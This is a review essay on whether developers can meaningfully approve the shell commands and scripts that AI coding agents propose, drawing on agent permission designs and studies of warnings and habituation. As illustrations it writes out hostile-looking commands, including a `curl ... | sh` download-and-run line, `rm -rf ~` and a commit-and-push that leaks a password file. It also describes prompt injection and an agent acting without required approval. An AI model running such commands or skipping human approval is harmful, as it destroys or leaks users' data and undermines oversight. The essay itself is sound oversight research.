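# Whether people can meaningfully approve the shell commands and scripts that AI agents propose

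## What an approval prompt asks of a person

An AI agent is a system that carries out a task in steps by using tools. Its most general tool on a computer is the shell, a program that reads a line of text, called a shell command, and has the operating system run one or more other programs. Coding agents such as Anthropic's Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex constantly issue shell commands to list files, install packages, run tests and save versions of the code. They also write scripts, which are files of instructions that run as programs, and start them with shell commands. Much of this happens on the user's own machine, where the agent can reach the user's files and sometimes passwords, so many of these products pause before some actions and show an approval prompt, which is a request that the user can allow or refuse.

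An approval prompt puts a person's judgement between what the agent proposes and what the computer does. Agents misread tasks and make mistakes. They can also follow instructions planted in a web page, file or email they read, an attack known as prompt injection. *How Agents Ask for Permission* (Michael and Roesner, 2026) surveys 21 proposed systems that let users control what agents may do. Fifteen of the proposals describe a threat, and ten of those assume a benign agent that makes mistakes or follows planted text. How well a prompt protects against that threat depends on how well the person judges the proposed action.

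### One ordinary request

A developer has asked an agent to fix a bug in a JavaScript program. The agent reads some files, edits one of them, and now needs to check whether the fix works. Anthropic's documentation for Claude Code shows the prompt a developer would see at roughly this point. A box titled "Bash command" (Bash is a widely used shell) contains the description "Run the test suite", followed by the command `npm test` and a question asking whether the developer wants to proceed. The developer can choose yes; yes, and stop asking about `npm test *`; yes, and switch to auto mode; or no. They can add a comment to a plain yes or no. After a refusal, the agent continues if the developer has added a comment, which it receives as the reason, and otherwise stops.

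A plain yes and the "don't ask again" option sit next to each other in the same short list, and each takes one keystroke, but they differ a good deal in what they grant. A plain yes covers one run. "Don't ask again" creates an allow rule, a standing permission that lets matching commands run without a prompt. The asterisk in this rule stands for any text, so the rule covers `npm test` with anything after it, in every later session in the same project. It has no end date, whereas an approval to edit files lapses when the session ends. Auto mode goes further and hands most such decisions to a classifier, a separate AI model that reviews the agent's actions and blocks those it rates unsafe.

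A command's text may not show what it will run. `npm test` tells npm, a tool that manages JavaScript projects, to run whatever is listed under "test" in one of the project's files. That is nearly always a harmless test program, but the agent may have changed that entry or the tests a minute earlier, and the prompt would look the same.

### Why the shell is a special case

A phone's request to let an app use the camera names one resource, but permission to use the shell doesn't name any. In Claude Code's permission rules, the single word `Bash` matches every command, and a command can start any program the user could start. Anthropic explains that shell access can therefore get around other restrictions. If a user limits the agent's web-fetching tool to one site but allows shell commands, the agent can still reach any address with a program such as `curl`. A rule against reading a certain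 file applies to Claude Code's own file tools and the file commands it recognises, such as `cat`, but not to a Python script that opens the file itself. To block the script, the user needs a sandbox, which is a set of limits that the operating system enforces on running programs.

Vendors therefore divide the shell into smaller permissions. According to the May 2026 version of Anthropic's *Configure permissions*, Claude Code requires approval for shell commands and file edits but not for reading files. A fixed list of read-only commands, such as `ls` and `grep`, also runs without a prompt. Claude Code splits a compound command (several commands on one line) and requires permission for each part, and choosing "don't ask again" for such a line can save up to five rules. Commands that are too complex for this analysis, or longer than 10,000 characters, always require the person's approval in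 Manual mode. This last rule is awkward because it leaves people to review the commands that the software couldn't analyze.

An allow rule meant for safe commands can also admit destructive ones. `devbox run` executes whatever command follows it, so a rule allowing `devbox run *` also allows `devbox run rm -rf` followed by a folder's name, which deletes the folder and everything inside. The person who clicked "don't ask again" on a harmless build step may never have thought of that.

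OpenAI describes a different arrangement for Codex. A sandbox limits what commands can technically do, such as where they may write and whether they can reach the network. An approval policy sets when Codex must ask for approval, for example before a command leaves the sandbox or falls outside a trusted set. When a command would leave the sandbox, the person has the narrower decision of whether to allow that. They see fewer requests, and the ones they see matter more.

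### What current tools display

The broadest account of approval screens is *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent–Human Interaction Problem* (Wang, Li and Tian, 2026), which catalogued 21 production systems as they stood in April 2026. Fifteen of them pause for a person's approval during a task. Some screens show little more than a request to allow an action, with no context. Others print the raw command, or add a line on why the action counts as risky. File edits often come with a diff, which shows exactly which lines change, and a few products present a whole plan for approval or a summary that expands into detail. Wang and colleagues' main observation is that the informative displays go with file edits and plans, while approvals of single commands, which dominate daily use, mostly come with a raw command on one line. They describe information as shallowest in this case.

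Wang and colleagues catalogue the options that approval prompts offer. The simplest prompts only let a person allow or deny an action. The most common design can also remember an approval for the session or permanently, which widens what the agent may do without asking. Few products make it easy to narrow these permissions again, and the researchers found none that showed users how much the permissions had expanded during a session. A rarer design, in the LangChain toolkit for building agents, lets the person edit the action before approving it.

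This survey relies on public documentation, and one researcher classified most of the systems, with spot checks by another. The products also change weekly. The survey lists Claude Code under raw command text, but the current documentation shows a short description above the command. A larger change affects how often the prompt appears. Soldani (2026), in *Claude Code Complete User Handbook*, checked the product's documentation on 12 November 2026 and reports that interactive sessions in the terminal and the VS Code editor now start in auto mode by default on every plan. The `npm test` box now appears mainly in Manual mode, which a user has to choose or an organisation has to impose. Approval records from Manual mode will increasingly describe people who wanted to be asked, and they may well be more careful than other users.

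In late May and early June 2026, Michael and Roesner tested the Claude and ChatGPT chatbots, the desktop agents Claude Cowork and Codex, and ChatGPT's agent mode, which operates a remote browser. They used a test Gmail account and a folder of files, so the results apply only indirectly to shell commands. Four of the five products asked for permission at least some of the time. Agent mode had no permission settings, gave users no chance to refuse, and opened Gmail freely. At the other extreme, ChatGPT's chat mode required approval for every action under a permission, and users could not grant it in advance.

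The most troubling result was that Claude created an email draft without asking, even though the setting for creating drafts was "Needs approval". The browser's log carried a flag that marked approval as unnecessary. The researchers reproduced this at least three times over June and July and reported it to Anthropic. The only other settings were "Always allow" and "Blocked", so users had no way to make sure they were asked every time. Codex has a similar automatic reviewer, but it is an explicit setting and is off by default. Commercial products change quickly and their inner workings are closed, so Claude may no longer behave this way. Even so, counting the prompts a person answered would miss actions like this one, which the person had no chance to stop.

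### Four conditions for meaningful approval

An approval is meaningful, in the sense that makes it a real check, when four conditions hold.

- Attention: the person looks at the request before answering it.
- Understanding: the person can tell its effects, meaning what the command will change, read or send on this particular machine.
- Comparison: the person holds those effects against what they wanted and would refuse if the command went further.
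- Faithful display: what the tool shows is what the tool then runs.

Meaningful approval requires a person to pay attention to a command, understand its effects, and judge whether those effects are safe in their situation. Any one of these can fail while the others hold. A developer who has approved forty test runs may approve the next command without reading it. Studies of browser and phone prompts have long documented this habituation, in which people respond less to something repeated, and in work with agents the resulting habit is called approval fatigue. A developer who reads every character may still not know that the option `-c` can make `git`, the standard tool for saving versions of code, run another program of the agent's choosing. Even an expert who understands a command may misjudge whether it is safe. Wang and colleagues give the example of a request to delete all `.tmp` files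 in a project. Its effect is plain, but its safety depends on how the user's project and workflow use those files, and no list of forbidden commands can settle that.

Whether a prompt accurately shows what the person is approving depends only on the tool. Claude Code offers "don't ask again" only where the prompt can show everything the new rule would allow. Before one of its file tools opens an approved file, it confirms that the path still leads where it did at the time of the check. Such precautions exist because things can change between the person's answer and the action. The clearest example is a script that the prompt shows by name, but whose contents have changed since the person last read it.

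Soldani suggests asking five questions before approving anything one did not write. Which exact files, account or host does the command touch? Does it name its target or rely on a broad wildcard? Can the user reverse it? Could it put a password or key into the output? Could a read-only command get the same information? These are sensible questions, but a person can't answer most of them from the text `npm test` alone. To answer them, they would have to open the project's files each time. Some prompts offer to explain a command on request, which reduces the work, but the person then has to judge the explanation too.

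### What the numbers measure

Four quantities recur in research on approval. The base rate, *b*, is the share of all requests that are in fact harmful. The unsafe approval rate, *u*, is the share of harmful requests that people approve. Its counterpart, *s*, is the share of harmless requests that they approve. The approval rate, *A*, is the share of all requests that they approve, harmful and harmless together. They fit together in one line:

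*A* = *b* × *u* + (1 − *b*) × *s*

When harmful requests are rare, the overall approval rate carries almost no information about the unsafe approval rate. Suppose that 10 requests in 1,000 are harmful. One developer reads them all and refuses the 10, along with 20 harmless ones out of caution. Another approves 97 in every 100 at random, without reading. Both approve 97 per cent of requests, but he lets through nine or ten of the harmful ones and she lets through none. The difference between the safe approval rate, *s*, and the unsafe approval rate, *u*, is about 98 percentage points for her and zero for him. However, two in three of her refusals stop legitimate work, which gives her some reason to become less careful.

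A low rate of unsafe approvals proves little on its own, since someone who refuses every request scores zero. *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (2026) therefore counts both the overreaching actions each permission scheme blocks and the required actions it lets the agent complete. It also measures the number of prompts and how much of the user's time they take.

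Calculating any of these rates except *A* requires someone to decide which requests were harmful, which a log of clicks doesn't show. Deleting a folder called `build` is routine in one project and a disaster in another, and often only the user knows which. Experimenters avoid this problem by planting requests designed to be harmful. They have to plant many more than real work would contain, because at a base rate of one in a thousand, a participant who answered fifty prompts would have only about a 5 per cent chance of seeing any. Participants who see several in an hour may become more watchful than they would be in their normal work, so these experiments may understate the unsafe approval rate.

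The kinds of evidence on the subject therefore test different conditions.

| Evidence | What it yields | Conditions it can test |
|---|---|---|
| Analysis of commands | How far the text settles the effects | Faithful display; the upper limit of understanding |
| Studies of browser and phone prompts | Whether people look, recall and comply | Attention; understanding of simpler requests |
| Usage records from agents | Approval rates, sometimes response times | Attention, by inference only |
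| Surveys and interviews | What people report doing | Attention and understanding, as people judge their own |
| Experiments with planted requests | Approval rates for harmful and harmless requests | Attention, understanding and comparison, mostly lumped together |
| Product walkthroughs | Whether a prompt appears and matches the action | Faithful display |

Direct evidence is scarcest for shell commands. According to *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), research has covered how developers set expectations for agents in advance much better than how they interpret and answer permission requests while the agent works. Comparison is the hardest condition to test under any method. In an experiment, the researcher usually assigns the task, so the participant checks a command against someone else's wishes, with someone else's files at stake. A developer at work checks it against her own half-formed intention,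 and may only decide what she wanted when she reads the request.

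## What the text of a command tells a reader and what it leaves out

Approval prompts for single commands mostly show the raw command, so its text limits how well even an attentive expert can understand what they are approving. Some commands state nearly all their effects, while others, like `npm test`, run instructions stored in another file. The problem comes up often, because shell commands make up more than 45 per cent of agents' tool calls in the real coding sessions analysed in *SWE-chat* (2026).

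### One command, part by part

Suppose a developer asks an agent to clear out old log files, and the agent proposes this line:

```
find . -name "*.log" -mtime +7 -print0 | xargs -0 rm -f && git add -A && git commit -m "cleanup" && git push
```

The line has four steps joined by `&&`, so each later step runs only if the one before it succeeded. One step deletes files, and the three `git` steps save changes and send them to another computer.

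`find .` searches the current folder, which the dot stands for, and every folder inside it. `-name "*.log"` keeps only names that end in `.log`. Without the quotation marks, the shell might replace the asterisk with matching names from the current folder before `find` starts. `-mtime +7` keeps only files last modified more than seven days ago, but the exact cutoff depends on the system. The usual Linux version of `find` ignores part-days, so a file qualifies after eight full days. The macOS version rounds part-days up, so a file qualifies as soon as it passes seven.

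`-print0` lists the matching names with an invisible character between them. The vertical bar passes that list to `xargs -0`, which splits it at the same character and adds the names to the end of `rm -f`. Without that character, names containing spaces would be split, so a file named `old report.log` would reach `rm` as `old` and `report.log`, and `rm` would delete any file with either name. `rm -f` deletes without asking for confirmation and doesn't move files to a recycle bin.

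`git add -A` selects every change in the repository for the next saved version. The repository is the folder of code whose history Git keeps. The selection includes new, edited and deleted files, except new files that the project's settings exclude. `git commit -m "cleanup"` saves that version, called a commit, with the title "cleanup". `git push` sends it to a copy of the repository on a server such as GitHub, along with any earlier commits on the same branch (a separate line of work) that the developer hasn't sent yet.

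### Facts missing from the line

A reader who knows all of this still can't tell which files will disappear or what will leave the machine, because the dot could stand for any folder. In a project's `logs` folder, the deletion is probably harmless. In the developer's home folder, it would remove old logs belonging to every program that keeps them there. `git add` would then probably fail, since few people keep their whole home folder in Git, but only after the logs were deleted.

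`git add -A` also covers the whole repository, even when run from a subfolder, whereas `find` works downwards from the current folder. Suppose the developer has a half-finished change to the login code and a file named `.env.backup` that holds a database password. The project's ignore list covers `.env` but not the backup. The line would commit both under the title "cleanup" and send them to the server. If the repository is public, anyone could then copy the password, even after a later commit deletes the file, because it stays in the history.

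Many projects configure Git to ignore log files. If this one does, the deletions wouldn't appear in the commit, Git couldn't restore the logs, and the "cleanup" commit would contain only the developer's other work. The commit would also contain only that work if no log file were old enough to delete, because an empty list doesn't count as a failure and the Git steps still run.

The command `git push` doesn't specify a server or a branch, because Git takes both from the repository's settings. The same command might send commits to a private branch that nobody else reads, or to the main branch that a company releases to its customers automatically.

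A developer can find out all of this with commands that change nothing:

| Missing fact | What depends on it | How to check |
|---|---|---|
| The current folder | Where the search for logs begins | `pwd` |
| The matching files | What `rm` deletes | `find . -name "*.log" -mtime +7` |
| Other changes in the repository | What the commit contains | `git status` |
| The branch, its destination and any unsent commits | What the push sends, and where | `git branch -vv` and `git remote -v` |

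These checks take a minute or so for someone who knows to run them. The developer can also refuse and ask the agent for a more explicit command. For example, `git add logs` limits the commit to one folder, and `git push origin log-cleanup` names the branch. Even then, the command doesn't show the address it pushes to, because `origin` is a nickname defined in the repository's settings.

### Small differences in text, large differences in effect

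A program's name is not enough to tell a reviewer what a command does. *FACET* (2026) analyses 39,136 commands from successful runs by an AI agent and finds that three programs, `cat`, `python3` and `ls`, account for 69.5 per cent of them. A reviewer could quickly learn what these programs are for, but would still need to check how each command uses them, because `cat notes.txt` displays a file while `cat > notes.txt` replaces its contents.

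The same command can have different effects depending on which files and folders exist. *ShellVis* (2026), which presents a tool for watching shell scripts run in a protected copy of the file system, gives the example of sorting photos into folders by year with `mv $f $year`, where `$f` is a photo and `$year` is the year it was taken. If a folder named `2022` exists, the command moves each 2022 photo into it. If there is no such folder, `mv` renames the first photo to `2022`, and each later photo from that year overwrites the one before, so all but one are lost. A reader can't tell from the command whether the folder exists.

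A single character can be just as destructive. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (Zhong, Liao and colleagues, 2026) examines 290 public reports of agents misusing files, from February 2024 to March 2026. In one, an agent tried to delete a file named `~`. The shell treats an unprotected `~` as the user's home folder, so the agent deleted that instead. In another, a misplaced quotation mark caused a command to wipe an entire drive. An expert looking for such errors would probably catch the tilde, but it is easy to miss at a glance.

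People are more likely to skim long commands. Zhong and colleagues show a Codex prompt for a very small job, replacing the word "hello" in one file. The proposed line first checks that the file exists and stops with an error message if it doesn't. It then makes the replacement and searches the file for the old and new words, ignoring any error from the search. Only the short `sed -i` command in the middle changes anything. The prompt also offers not to ask again about `sed -i`, which can edit any file the user can edit. *Is Bash All You Need?* (2026), a study of agents on workplace tasks, found that agents typically put several commands into each shell call.

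*NL2Bash* (2018), a collection of commands paired with English descriptions, leaves out commands that redirect output to files or set variables because they "need to be interpreted in context". Agents routinely write files with redirections such as `cat > notes.txt`.

### Commands that run code from somewhere else

`make clean && make` is a standard way to delete a program's old build files and rebuild it. The `make` program reads its instructions from a file called a Makefile, which lists the commands to run under names such as `clean`. *Shall We Approve?* (Wu, Chen and colleagues, 2026) compares two workspaces in which a user has asked for this cleanup. In one, `clean` deletes the `build` folder. In the other, it deletes the source code and the `.git` folder, which holds the project's history. The request and the proposed command are the same in both, so a person who sees only the approval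 prompt cannot tell which will happen.

`python3 setup.py` is even less informative. It runs the file `setup.py`, so a person who approves it approves whatever that file contains at that moment. Zhong and colleagues use this example for what they call uninformative approval, which they list as a contributing cause in 31 of the 290 reports. The reports come from security researchers and from people who had a problem and described it in public, so they can't show how often such prompts mislead people in ordinary use.

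Installing or building software can also run other people's code. `npm install`, with no package named, installs every package the project lists and every package those depend on, and npm allows packages to include scripts that run during installation. Python's installer, `pip`, may run a package's `setup.py` when it builds the package from source. Some package managers now block such scripts until the user allows them. Zhong and colleagues describe a possible attack in Rust, a programming language whose `cargo build` command can run scripts from the packages a project depends on. A malicious script could read the user's SSH key, which gives access to other machines, and change the shell's startup file, though the user would see only `cargo build`.

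Agents often run scripts. *What Makes Interaction Trajectories Effective for Training Terminal Agents?* (2026) counts 153,496 agent commands, excluding those used only to look around. About 25 per cent of them started Python, JavaScript or a shell to run code, and another 29 per cent wrote files with `cat`. These commands come from training data, so the shares may differ in everyday work. A reviewer sees a script's full text when an agent writes it with `cat`, but only its name when the agent runs it later.

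Wu and colleagues tested how this affects an AI model that reviews commands. They created 102 tasks in which a project's own tool secretly deletes or overwrites a file it should leave alone, and paired each with a harmless version that had the same request and command. When the model saw only the command, 44.1 per cent of the dangerous tasks still ended in harm, and the model blocked the main command in 52.0 per cent of the harmless versions. When it saw the full conversation, harm fell to 17.6 per cent, but it blocked 61.8 per cent of the harmless versions. Asking the model to predict the effects from the command and the files the command referred to cut harm to 3.9 per cent. It still blocked 61.8 per cent of the harmless versions, so it avoided harm largely by blocking commands indiscriminately.

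People might do better than this model, especially if they know the project. The benchmark is also deliberately hard, since the text in each pair is identical and tools that secretly destroy files are much more common than in real projects. However, some of the tools were compiled programs without source code, so even a reviewer who had time to open every file couldn't have read them.

### Why reading can't settle every case

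There is also a mathematical limit on what anyone can learn from a program's text. No checker can read any program and always determine correctly whether it would ever delete a file. If one existed, it could be used on a program that runs another program P, which only does calculations, and then deletes one file. The file is deleted only if P finishes, so the checker would also reveal whether P finishes. Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no general method can do that for every program. The same argument applies to other effects, such as sending a password to a server.

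The proof only rules out a method that is right about every program. People and software can still be right about most programs they meet, and they can refuse the ones they can't work out. Practical obstacles matter more from day to day. A program's behaviour may depend on the date, the contents of a file, or a reply from a server. `curl https://example.com/install.sh | sh` downloads a script and runs it immediately, and the server's owner can change that script after the person has looked at it. Some scripts also build new commands as they run, and *FACET*'s command-analysis software couldn't fully recover these.

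A careful reader can learn a lot from the text of a command. They can see which programs it starts and in what order, which files it names, and whether it uses the network or asks for administrator rights with `sudo`. For a familiar program with a named target, such as `ls src`, this tells them nearly everything the command will do. They can also see when a command runs code defined elsewhere, as `make`, `npm test` and `python3 setup.py` all do, and so know that they need to open another file. Reading the text is better for spotting danger than for ruling it out. A reader can refuse `rm -rf ~` on sight, but can't tell from `make test` alone whether it is safe.

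### Reading a generated script

Suppose an agent has written a 60-line Python script that copies old customer records into an archive and deletes the originals. SABER, one of the benchmarks that Wu and colleagues use, sorts the harm that coding agents can do into eight categories, from information leaks and destroyed data to persistence, meaning changes that keep acting after the task ends. With a few additions, those categories give a reviewer the following questions:

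- Which folder does the script run in, and does it work on the right files from there?
- Which files can it delete, move or overwrite, and where does each path come from?
- Does it read passwords, keys or personal data, and do any of them end up in its output or in another file?
- What does it send over the network, and to whom? Does it download anything and then run it?
- Does it ask for extra rights, or weaken any permissions, tests or security checks?
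- Does it leave anything running or scheduled?
- Which other scripts and packages does it use? The same questions apply to each of them.
- What happens if it stops halfway, or if someone runs it twice?
- Does it do what the developer asked, and only that?

One line can take several minutes to check. Suppose a script contains `shutil.rmtree(os.path.join(base, name))`, which deletes the folder called `name` inside the folder `base`. If `name` is empty, Python deletes all of `base`. If `name` begins with a slash, Python ignores `base` and deletes whatever folder `name` gives. The reviewer therefore has to find out where `name` comes from. It may come from a spreadsheet, in which case its value isn't in the script.

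A common rule of thumb for careful code inspection is 200 to 400 lines an hour, so a 60-line script would take roughly 9 to 18 minutes, though one with many routine lines may go faster. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (2026) reports an experiment with office tasks in which the median approval decision took between 16.3 and 38.6 seconds, depending on the screen. Those requests involved emails, documents and purchases, so they don't show how long people would spend on a script. But a reviewer who spent 38.6 seconds on 60 lines would have less than two-thirds of a second for each line.

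If an agent writes ten such scripts in a day, reading them at the inspection rate would take an hour and a half to three hours. Developers use agents to save time, so few are likely to read them that carefully.

A quicker approach is to search the script for dangerous operations and read only the lines around them. This takes a minute or two and will catch many careless mistakes, but the reviewer has to know every way to perform each operation. Zhong and colleagues list several ways to delete a file, including `rm`, `unlink`, `find -delete`, and Python's `os.remove`. Their list omits `shutil.rmtree`, which deletes a whole folder, so a reviewer who searched only for the listed names would miss it.

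### Whether people understand code that agents wrote

Even with enough time to read a script, a person can misunderstand it. *(Im)Paired Programming* (Balepur, Baumler and colleagues, 2026) compared students who had an agent write their code with students who mostly wrote it themselves. The 54 computer science students, from two US colleges, each had up to 50 minutes to build a web game, a variant of noughts and crosses on a five-by-five board. The researchers randomly gave half of them an agent that edited the code directly. The others had a chatbot that offered only general help and short snippets, so they had to write or adapt the code. Everyone then answered up to 12 unannounced questions about their own code.

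The agent group built more accurate games and finished faster, but scored much lower on the questions overall. The gap was large by the usual statistical standard (Cohen's *d* above 0.80). Its size depended on the type of question:

| Task in the question | Agent group | Chatbot group |
|---|---|---|
| Pick out names that appear in one's own code | 70% | 79% |
| Choose one's own code from two equivalent snippets | 59% | 96% |
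| Explain what a snippet is for | 63% | 86% |
| Predict what would happen if the code changed | 74% | 75% |

Guessing would give 50 per cent on the question about equivalent snippets, so the agent group barely recognised their own code. That result depends partly on memory, however, and a person answering an approval prompt has at least some text to read. The question about purpose is closer to approval because participants could see the snippet, and the agent group still did considerably worse. The most encouraging result for approval came from the question about changes, where participants had to predict behaviour and the two groups did equally well. Balepur and colleagues suggest that these questions may have been too easy, or that people who work with an agent can understand how the website behaves without understanding its code.

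Scores also varied with review habits. Agent users who accepted changes one file at a time averaged 78 per cent on the questions, which was still below the chatbot group's average. Those who clicked "Accept All" averaged 66 per cent, and those who let changes through automatically averaged 62 per cent. These groups were small and overlapping. The file-by-file reviewers also scored higher on the test of background knowledge, so skilled people may simply review more carefully.

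In both groups, participants' ratings of how well they understood their code tended to match their scores. The agent group rated their understanding lower than the chatbot group did, but still preferred the agent. If the same holds for approval, many people who approve a script they don't understand probably know they don't understand it.

A smaller study, *Beyond the Prompt* (Qiao, Haque and Hundhausen, 2026), found a similar pattern among ten professional developers who averaged 6.5 years of experience and used AI coding tools daily. Each worked with GitHub Copilot, a coding agent, on an unfamiliar application of about 67,000 lines. They had up to two hours and 15 minutes to complete six tasks, which the researchers checked with 136 automatic tests. In interviews during the session, the developers explained how they had worked and how their solution functioned. Three AI models graded the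 explanations for the first two tasks, with a maximum total of 14.

Of the ten developers, four passed many tests and explained their work well, and four did worse on both. One of the other two passed 112 tests but scored zero for understanding, and told the researchers, "No understanding; I didn't really look at any files." The other passed only 31 tests but scored 10 out of 14 for understanding. A working result therefore isn't good evidence that the person understands the code behind it.

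The four developers who did well on both counts spent 1.5 per cent of their time looking at code. They spent about a quarter of the session watching the agent work, and they often checked the running application or ran tests themselves. This suggests that people can learn what a program does by watching it, without reading much of its code. A study of ten people is too small to establish that, and the researchers make no claim beyond this group. The approach also works poorly for approving commands. A developer can run a web page repeatedly and fix what looks wrong, but a command that deletes files may do its damage on the first run.

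Both studies tested people after they had accepted the code, and both used web applications. There is less evidence on how well people understand shell commands. *RACONTEUR* (2024), which introduces an AI tool that explains shell commands, asked people to rate how much explanations of 20 malicious and 20 harmless commands helped them understand each command and tell whether it was malicious. Such ratings measure how useful people find an explanation, but they can't show whether people understood the command correctly.

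Researchers could test readers directly by showing them a command and a list of the files on the machine, asking what will have changed after it runs, and then running it to check their answers. The `mv $f $year` example would work well because the right answer depends on whether the folders exist. A reader could know what `mv` does and still answer incorrectly by not checking the list.

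## Studies of permission prompts and warnings in browsers and phones

Even a command that states its effects clearly protects only people who read it. The best evidence on whether people read requests comes from web browsers and phones, which were interrupting users with warnings and permission requests long before coding agents existed. Their designers have also tried remedies on millions of users, which gives some idea of what might work for agents.

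### What phone users noticed and understood

Until 2015, Android listed an app's permissions on the last screen before installation, and a person could accept the whole list or cancel. To study this screen, Felt, Ha and colleagues, in *Android Permissions* (2012), surveyed 308 Android users online and watched 25 others install apps on their own phones in a coffee shop. To keep people from thinking about security, the researchers introduced themselves as computer science students and asked each person to find a coupon app. They noted whether the person mentioned or clicked on the permissions, and then asked what the previous page had contained.

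Of the 24 people whose behaviour the researchers could classify, four (17 per cent) looked at the permissions. Ten knew the page listed them but didn't look this time, and ten didn't know they were there. In the survey, 17.5 per cent of people said they had looked during their last installation. The coffee-shop sample is small, but the rate observed there is close to the rate people reported in the survey.

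Three of the ten who knew about the permissions volunteered that they used to look at them but had stopped. At the time, about 90 per cent of apps requested at least one permission. One participant had worried about apps having access to her location until she saw how many requested it.

Few survey respondents understood the permissions. Each answered three questions, drawn from a set of eleven, about what a permission would let an app do. Eight of 302 people got all three right, and the average score was 21 per cent. An answer counted only if it included every correct choice and no wrong one, and 53 per cent of answers contained at least one correct choice. Some mistakes probably came from the large headings above each permission. Android put the permission to make phone calls under "Services that cost you money", and almost as many people thought it let the app charge their credit card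 as thought it let the app make calls. People who said they read permissions still averaged only 30.3 per cent, against 18.6 per cent for the rest.

The permission screen did help a minority. Five of the 25 people in the coffee shop could describe a specific time when permissions had made them cancel an installation.

People also respond to what a request looks like. Böhme and Köpsell (2010), in *Trained to accept*, showed 12 versions of a consent dialog to 80,000 users of an online privacy tool. Fewer people agreed when the wording was polite or the buttons made the choice look voluntary. More agreed when the dialog looked like a software licence agreement, the long legal text that most people accept without reading. They seem to have recognised the type of dialog and given their usual answer. Users of a privacy tool may well care more than most people about what they agree to.

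A button's design can have a similar effect. After the European Union's data protection law took effect in 2018, many websites began to ask visitors which uses of cookies they would allow. Machuletz and Böhme (2019), in *Multiple Purposes, Multiple Problems*, compared versions of such a dialog in a classroom experiment. People who saw a default button that accepted every purpose at once agreed to more purposes than the control group. They also recalled their choices less accurately and regretted them more often.

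### Twenty-five million browser warnings

Browsers warn users about sites that spread malicious software and about phishing sites, which imitate real ones to steal passwords. They also show an SSL or certificate warning when they can't confirm that they have reached the real site. Someone may be intercepting the connection, but often the site's owner has only set up the server badly. *Alice in Warningland* (Akhawe and Felt, 2013) used data from Chrome and Firefox to study how people responded to 25.4 million warnings of all three kinds in May and June 2013. People saw these warnings during their ordinary browsing, not while playing a role in a study.

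| Warning | Continued past it in Firefox | Continued past it in Chrome |
|---|---|---|
| Malicious software | 7.2% | 23.2% |
| Phishing | 9.1% | 18.0% |
| Certificate | 33.0% | 70.2% |

Most people turned back at five of the six warnings, which contradicts the common belief that people ignore every warning. The two kinds of danger warning are almost always right. Both browsers took their lists of dangerous sites from the same service, and Akhawe and Felt treat its false alarms as negligible. Certificate warnings, by contrast, often appear on harmless sites, so people who continue usually come to no harm.

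Chrome's certificate warning included the specific problem, so Akhawe and Felt could compare the three most common problems. People dismissed the warning most often and fastest when it was for the most common problem.

| Problem with the certificate | Share of Chrome's certificate warnings | Continued | Time within which about half of those who continued had clicked |
|---|---|---|---|
| Unknown issuer | 56.0% | 81.8% | 1.7 seconds |
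| Name doesn't match the site | 25.0% | 62.8% | 2.2 seconds |
| Expired | 17.6% | 57.4% | 2.7 seconds |

Akhawe and Felt read this as a sign of warning fatigue. Another possible explanation is that regular visitors expect the unknown-issuer warning, since it is often a permanent feature of a site, such as a company's internal page. An expired certificate appears on a site that worked yesterday, and the surprise may make people stop. Both explanations could be true, and these data aren't enough to tell them apart.

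Extra clicks did little to stop people. Firefox's certificate warning took three clicks to pass, and 84 per cent of people who made the first two also made the third. More people passed Chrome's warnings about malicious sites, which took two clicks, than Firefox's, which took one. Akhawe and Felt suggest that people decide once and then click as many times as they need to. People clicked Chrome's "Help me understand" button on only 1.6 per cent of certificate warnings, and nobody opened the technical details in Firefox.

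Part of the gap between the browsers arises because Firefox remembered a person's decision to trust a site, while Chrome asked again on every visit. Akhawe and Felt give the example of someone who turns back from one site and visits another nine times despite its faulty certificate. That person would click through one of two warnings in Firefox (50 per cent) and nine of ten in Chrome (90 per cent). Approval rates for coding agents should be read with the same caution, because an allow rule removes prompts that the user would have approved. Two developers with identical judgement can have very different approval rates if one of them uses "don't ask again".

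Laboratory studies had made people look more careless. Akhawe and Felt review two experiments in which between 55 and 80 per cent of participants continued past a slightly older version of Firefox's certificate warning. In the later experiment, 46 per cent of participants said they continued because they felt safe in the laboratory or wanted to finish the task. In a separate 2007 experiment, 53 per cent of participants clicked past a warning on a bank's website, but 36 per cent of those who used their own passwords did so. In experiments on agents, too, participants may take less care than they would outside the laboratory.

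### Requests that phone users would have refused

A prompt protects people only if it appears when they would object. To find those moments, Wijesekera, Baokar and colleagues (2015), in *Android Permissions Remystified*, lent 36 people modified phones for a week. The phones recorded every use of a protected resource, such as location or text messages, and took occasional screenshots when an app used one of 12 sensitive permissions. At the end of the week, participants looked at their screenshots, learned which app had used which permission, and said whether they would have stopped it.

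The 36 participants would have blocked 149 of 423 requests, or 35 per cent, although the apps already had permission for all of them. Thirty participants would have blocked at least one. In 53 per cent of the cases they wanted to block, they thought the app didn't need the data for what it was doing, and in about a third they considered the data too private. They thought 71 per cent of the requests they would have allowed were necessary for the app to work. On a five-point scale of how expected they were, the requests participants would have allowed averaged 3.2, compared with 2.3 for those they would have blocked.

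Several of the same researchers later studied 131 people for an average of 32 days each, prompting them on their own phones when apps used sensitive permissions. The participants wanted to block 60 per cent of the requests. That figure and the one from the earlier study are far above the share that people refused when refusing meant giving up the app.

In the recordings, apps used the 12 sensitive permissions 213 times an hour per person, which is too often for a phone to ask every time. Asking only the first time can allow uses the person never considered. Three-quarters of the recorded requests came when the person had no sign that the app was running, so a permission given while using a map could also cover tracking at night. An allow rule for an agent carries the same risk, because it can also cover later commands the person didn't have in mind.

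*A Large Scale Study of User Behavior, Expectations and Engagement* (Cao, Xia and colleagues, 2021) followed 1,719 people in ten countries and regions for 30 days and recorded their real permission decisions. People were more than twice as likely to refuse a request they didn't expect. When an app explained why it wanted a permission, they refused about half as often. The explanations may have helped people see that a request was reasonable, or may just have reassured them. The app that wants the permission writes the explanation, much as an agent writes the description above its own command.

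### How repetition wears attention down

Most animals habituate, meaning that their brains spend less effort on a signal after meeting it many times without consequence. This is usually useful, because nobody could work while attending to every background sound and flicker. Habituation is involuntary, so it happens even to people who want to stay alert. It differs from reasoning that a warning can be skipped because it has always been a false alarm.

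Bravo-Lillo, Cranor and colleagues (2013), in *Your Attention Please*, habituated people to a dialog within a few minutes. Online workers had five minutes to answer the same dialog as many times as they could. A line in the dialog showed how many they had answered, and only "yes" was available. Then the line changed to an instruction to choose "no". With an ordinary dialog, 14 per cent of people followed the instruction the first time it appeared. The line had changed with every dialog as the count went up, but people had learned that it never mattered.

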